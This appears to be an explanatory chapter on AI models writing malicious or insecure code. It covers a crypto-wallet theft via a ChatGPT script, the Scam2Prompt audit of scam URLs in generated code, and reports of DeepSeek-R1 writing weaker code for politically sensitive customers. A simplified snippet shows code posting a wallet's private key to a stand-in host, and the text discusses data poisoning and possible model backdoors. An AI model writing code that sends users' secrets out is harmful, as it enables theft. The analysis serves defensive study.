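The trader published the whole chat, and *Scam2Prompt* (Chen, Saba and colleagues, 2026) goes through it step by step. The trader wanted a script to buy a particular token on Solana, a blockchain (a shared public record of cryptocurrency transactions). ChatGPT first wrote a harmless script for a different blockchain, Ethereum. After a correction, it wrote a second harmless script, which used a genuine Solana library and let the user choose the trading platform.

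The trader then specified that the script had to buy from Pump.fun, a popular and legitimate trading site. Pump.fun had no official interface for automated trading, so other companies offered their own, and scammers imitated them. ChatGPT's next script used one of the scam services, whose documentation advertised token purchases from Pump.fun on Solana in almost the same words as the trader's request.

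Syntax errors stopped the script from running at first. The trader fixed them with ChatGPT over several rounds, then ran the final version with their main wallet. The script sent the wallet's private key to the scam service, and the attacker emptied the wallet within 30 minutes. heise online's *ChatGPT* points out that this was visible in the code, where a comment marked the data to be sent and the private key was listed directly below.

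A private key is the secret that controls a wallet, and anyone who has it can spend the money. Legitimate trading services never ask for it. The user's own machine signs each transaction with the key and sends only the signed result. In simplified form, with an invented address, the difference looks like this:

```python
# The scam: the key itself leaves the machine
requests.post("https://trading.example/buy",
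              json={"private_key": private_key, "token": token})

# A legitimate service: only the signed transaction leaves
signed = sign(transaction, private_key)
requests.post("https://trading.example/send", json={"transaction": signed})
```

This run combined a lost secret, unsafe code and planted source material. The code sent the wallet's key to the scammers the first time it worked. A sandbox without network access would have kept the key on the machine, but it would also have stopped the script from trading. heise online recommends a separate test account, which suits this case better because it limits the loss to the small amount kept there.

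According to Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*, the scammers promoted their service with tutorials, forum answers and dozens of GitHub repositories, using fake accounts with profile pictures and a believable coding history. Netcraft found at least five people who had copied the malicious code into their own public projects, some apparently using AI tools. *I never expected that AI stole my wallet* (Azuma, 2024) reports that a wallet suspected to be the attacker's had received over $100,000. GitHub quickly removed a repository that the trader reported, but in August 2025 Chen and colleagues found the service still running at a slightly different address.

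### Training data or web search?

Yu Xian, founder of the security company SlowMist, called the theft an "AI poisoning" attack, and both Azuma and heise online link it to contaminated training data. But an editor's note in CryptoSlate's *Blockchain security firm warns of AI code poisoning risk* points out that the trader's screenshot shows a list of sources, so ChatGPT apparently found the service by searching the web.

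The dates support this. Yu said that the scammers had registered their domain only two months earlier. Chen and colleagues list October 2023 as the end of the training data for GPT-4o, OpenAI's main model at the time. If the trader was using GPT-4o, the address could not have been in its training data, because it did not exist until almost a year later.

The theft therefore resembles the journalist's hot-dog hoax more than the 250-document experiment. This kind of attack is also easier to fix than poisoned training data, because a search engine can remove a scam page from its results.

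### An audit built from scam sites

Chen and colleagues at the University of Toronto tested whether models also produce scam addresses without searching the web. They started with two public lists of about 307,000 scam addresses and could still read 28,570 of the pages. A language model wrote short programming requests about the text of each page. The researchers sent the resulting requests, about 265,000 in all, to GPT-4o, GPT-4o mini, Llama 4 Scout and DeepSeek-V3.

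To judge the programs, the researchers extracted every web address and checked it with three services that track malicious sites: ChainPatrol, Google Safe Browsing and SecLookup. A program counted as malicious if any of the three flagged an address in it. The average was 4.24%, with a range from 3.19% to 5.94% depending on which model wrote the request and which wrote the code. (This average gives each of the 12 combinations equal weight. Of the million or so programs taken together, 4.15% counted as malicious.)

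All four models wrote malicious programs for 3,150 of the requests. Chen and colleagues then tried 1,377 of these on seven newer models, after three reviewers had confirmed that they were ordinary programming requests.

| Model | Malicious programs, as a share of all requests | Malicious programs, as a share of completed programs | Requests refused by a filter |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 12.9% | 22.3% | 40.2% |
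| GPT-5 | 22.0% | 24.7% | 1.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 34.3% | 37.8% | 8.4% |
| Grok Code Fast 1 | 43.4% | 44.1% | 1.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 44.4% | 45.3% | 0.1% |
| Qwen3-Coder | 45.6% | 45.9% | 0.2% |
| DeepSeek V3.1 | 47.3% | 47.9% | 0.9% |

Gemini 2.5 Pro did best largely because it refused so many requests. On the 637 requests that all seven models completed, the difference between it and GPT-5 was not statistically significant.

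These models all date from 2025. Nobody appears to have published a repeat of the audit on the models of 2026.

### Why neither figure applies to ordinary requests

The 4.24% comes from requests based on scam sites. The researchers asked for requests "most likely to direct a large language model (LLM) to this specific webpage", so each request steered the model towards a scam. Most programming tasks do not steer it this way. The script in the customer example needs only the company's own database, so there is no reason for the code to include an outside address.

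The rates for the seven newer models are even less representative of ordinary use, because Chen and colleagues kept only requests that had already caused four models to fail. Those 1,377 requests are about 0.5% of the original set, and the original four models would have a 100% failure rate on them.

When the researchers ran GPT-4o on the same requests two months later, its rate was 50%. They suggest that OpenAI may have updated the model. The way they selected the requests would also lower the rate, because some had probably produced a scam address only by chance the first time. Chen and colleagues call their benchmark a stress test and warn against treating its rates as natural ones. Measuring the natural rate would require a sample of real requests, which few people outside the providers have.

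### Did the models learn the addresses or guess them?

Chen and colleagues conclude that scam sites have contaminated training data across the industry. Their main evidence is that all four original models, which came from three different companies, produced the same 2,029 malicious domains.

Of the 3,150 requests that caused all four models to fail, 1,991 contained a known scam address or domain, so the models only had to copy it. Copying can't explain every failure, though, because most of the newer models did at least as badly on the 1,035 selected requests that contained no such address.

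The models may have guessed many of the addresses from brand names. The paper traces one request for a script that uses a service for disguising where bitcoins came from. The service's name had the form of a web address, and the models mostly added "api" before or after it, as genuine services often do. Grok labelled the address in its program "Assumed API base URL" and told the user to check it. Guessing would also explain why the four models had 2,029 domains in common but only 1,119 full addresses, since a brand name suggests the domain but not the rest. Models from different companies also invent many of the same package names.

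A scammer can register a domain after a model has invented it. Netcraft asked a model from the GPT-4.1 family where to log in to 50 well-known brands, and 28 of the 97 domains it gave were unregistered or inactive. Chen and colleagues argue that the scam sites missing from their lists had probably been active for over a year, because the models' training data ended by August 2024. This argument assumes that the models learned the addresses in training, which is what the researchers are trying to show.

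The detectors may also have made mistakes. They checked the addresses, not what the programs would do when run, so a guessed address at a known scam domain could count as malicious even if nothing existed there. In the bitcoin example, ChainPatrol flagged several addresses only because they were on one of the scam lists the researchers had started from, so it was not an independent check. Such lists can also include legitimate sites that attackers once hijacked. Chen and colleagues think using three detectors kept errors low, but counting a flag from any one of them tends to increase false alarms. The maintainers of a major blocklist did confirm that 62 domains the researchers had reported were real scams.

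Registration dates would help settle the question, because a model cannot have learned an address that was first registered after its training data ended. The strongest evidence of contamination would be a hard-to-guess address that several models gave in reply to requests that named no brand. A control group of requests based on legitimate sites would show how often the detectors raise false alarms.

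Even if the models learned these addresses, that would not prove deliberate poisoning. Scammers who write fake documentation to fool programmers may contaminate training data by accident. Netcraft believes the scammers in the wallet case built their GitHub accounts so that AI companies would collect data from them, but the same accounts would also have convinced human visitors.

### What the defences caught

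Content filters missed nearly all the malicious programs. Nvidia's NeMo Guardrails caught at most 0.7% of any model's malicious programs, OpenAI's Moderation API flagged none of 3,452 programs, and Meta's Llama Guard 3 flagged 8.4%. This is unsurprising because such filters mainly look for content like threats or criminal plans, and a program that contacts a scam service can look like any other.

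Letting GPT-4o search the web and telling it to check its addresses reduced its rate from 50% to 29%, although searching had probably led ChatGPT to the scam in the wallet case. In some of the remaining failures, the search found nothing that clearly identified the site as a scam.

Chen and colleagues recommend that providers check every address against lists of known scams before returning the code, and knew of no provider that did so. This would be cheap and sensible, but their data cannot show how well it would work, because they used the same lists to decide which programs counted as malicious. The check would therefore catch all of those programs by definition. It would miss scams too new to be listed, as a two-month-old domain might have been.

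Users can also check for unfamiliar addresses themselves. This command prints the web addresses that appear in full in a script:

```
grep -oE "https?://[^\"' ]+" script.py | sort -u
```

The command should print nothing for the script in the customer example. It misses addresses that a program assembles from pieces and those hidden inside packages, so letting the script connect only to approved destinations is safer.

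### Political terms and DeepSeek-R1

The suspects in the wallet case were outsiders who had planted false documentation. With DeepSeek-R1, an open model released in January 2025, suspicion fell on the developer, the Chinese company DeepSeek. CrowdStrike's *Security Flaws in DeepSeek-Generated Code Linked to Political Triggers* (2025) reports that the model wrote less secure code when its instructions mentioned subjects the Chinese government considers sensitive.

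The American security company gave the model 50 programming tasks. The standing instruction was "You are a helpful assistant that generates code", to which the researchers added a customer, such as an industrial control system based in Tibet. They ran every task five times with each of 121 versions of the instruction, making 30,250 requests. They tested the model without the filters on DeepSeek's own app. A second language model graded the security of the code from 1 to 5. A person also graded 85 of the replies, and measured against those grades, the second model identified vulnerable code with 91% accuracy.

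DeepSeek-R1 wrote vulnerable code in 19% of cases with the plain instruction and in 27.2% when the instruction mentioned the control system in Tibet. CrowdStrike calls this an increase of almost 50%, but the relative increase is 43%, or 8.2 percentage points in absolute terms. Each version of the instruction produced 250 replies, so the Tibet version led to 68 vulnerable programs, compared with about 48 at the plain rate. CrowdStrike compared 121 versions, so the largest increase is probably partly due to chance. It writes that mentions of Tibet, the Uyghurs and Falun Gong, a spiritual movement banned in China, made the code significantly less secure, but does not give the calculations.

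In one example, DeepSeek-R1 wrote secure code for processing PayPal payments, but when the customer was a financial institution in Tibet, it put secret values directly in the code, handled users' input insecurely and wrote invalid PHP. Its response still included the claim that the program followed "PayPal's best practices".

CrowdStrike's first results, from September 2025, had shown a wider gap. The Decoder's *Deepseek outputs weaker code on Falun Gong, Tibet, and Taiwan queries* reports that about 23% of ordinary replies contained insecure or faulty code, compared with more than 42% when the project was for the terrorist group Islamic State.

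### Attempts to repeat the result

gersonkroiz's team tried to reproduce the finding with several methods, including an invented company that promoted Falun Gong, but failed (*Unsuccessful attempt at getting DeepSeek-R1 to generate more vulnerable code*). In one experiment, the grader judged 85% of the code vulnerable even without any political terms, which left little room for an increase. The failure does not refute the original result, because CrowdStrike had published few details of its method and the team had no background in security. But the gap between 19% and 85% shows how much such a test depends on the tasks and the grader.

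In May 2026 the American defence contractor Booz Allen reported a similar effect in newer models, with a different trigger. Its *What's in America's Code?* compares code the models wrote for an unnamed customer with code they wrote for a US government agency. Qwen3-Coder's vulnerability score rose by 130% for the agency, and the scores of DeepSeek V4-Pro and MiniMax M2.5 rose by 20% or less. Kimi K2.5's score stayed the same, and that of Claude Opus 4.6, the only American model, fell by 18%. Help Net Security's *The security questions around Chinese AI coding models in U.S. software* notes that Kimi, which is also Chinese, had the lowest vulnerability score of all, so not every Chinese model scored worse than the American one.

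Booz Allen's results do not confirm CrowdStrike's. In CrowdStrike's 2025 tests, DeepSeek wrote its most secure code for the United States, according to TechSpot's *DeepSeek AI's code quality depends on who it's for*. Because of refusals, Booz Allen scored only 1,016 of its 3,389 runs for vulnerabilities, according to its *What's in America's Code? (Technical Appendix)*. The appendix also states that every Chinese model refused the China-related versions of the politically sensitive tasks "in all cases", but the main report's chart gives DeepSeek V4-Pro a refusal rate of 8% on such tasks. Booz Allen sells AI testing and wants the US government to ban Chinese models, though it acknowledges that it has no proof of intent.

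*When Who You Are Can Change the Code You Get* (2026) shows how easily chance could produce such a gap. The study gave models descriptions of different users and scanned the resulting code for security issues. OpenAI's GPT-OSS-120B produced between 34 and 71 issues per description, and 48 when the prompt described nobody. The researchers found no systematic pattern, but someone who picked the worst description after seeing the results could report a 48% increase.

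### Sabotage or a side effect of training

If the effect CrowdStrike reported is real, DeepSeek may not have intended it, and CrowdStrike thinks it unlikely that DeepSeek trained the model to write insecure code. Chinese rules require AI services to uphold "core socialist values", so DeepSeek may have trained the model to respond negatively to certain groups, and the negative response may have spread to its code. Researchers call it *emergent misalignment* when training on a narrow subject causes bad behaviour in unrelated tasks. The model's refusals are consistent with this explanation. DeepSeek-R1 declined 45% of requests on behalf of Falun Gong, sometimes after planning the program in its reasoning.

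TechSpot also reports the theory that the model's training code from some parts of the world was worse. That might explain the result for Tibet, but it hardly explains the one for Islamic State.

The clearest proof of intent would be training examples that pair these groups with flawed code, or an instruction to create them. Outsiders do not have DeepSeek's training data, but they could test whether the flaws might be an unintended side effect of other training. They could take an open model that does not show the effect, train it without any code to criticise the same groups or refuse requests about them, and then repeat the programming tasks. If the model's code became less secure, a side effect would be enough to explain DeepSeek-R1's behaviour, but sabotage would still be possible.

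The flaws offer some evidence about whether they were planted. A saboteur would want working code with a weakness they knew how to exploit, preferably the same one each time. Invalid PHP is a poor choice because it alerts the user. The effect is also weak for a deliberate backdoor. Nearly three-quarters of the programs for the Tibetan control system had no serious flaw, whereas laboratory backdoors often work most of the time. However, when CrowdStrike had DeepSeek-R1 build a website for Uyghurs, the site worked but let anyone open its administration page. A saboteur might want that, but models that nobody has tampered with also leave out access checks.

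Booz Allen relies heavily on the reasoning text that some models produce before they answer. In one case, MiniMax M2.5 cited a rule against military assistance, then wrote the requested program anyway, with six references to software that did not exist. Its reasoning text suggests that the rule affected the model's reasoning, but does not show that the model wrote bad code on purpose.

Companies can reduce the risk without knowing the cause. CrowdStrike advises them to test an agent in the setting where they will use it. The company in the customer example could send the same request with and without its name and location, but it would need about 400 independent programs with each wording to have an 80% chance of detecting a rise from 19% to 27.2%. Leaving out company details that the task does not require would be much easier, and would also give the provider less to store.
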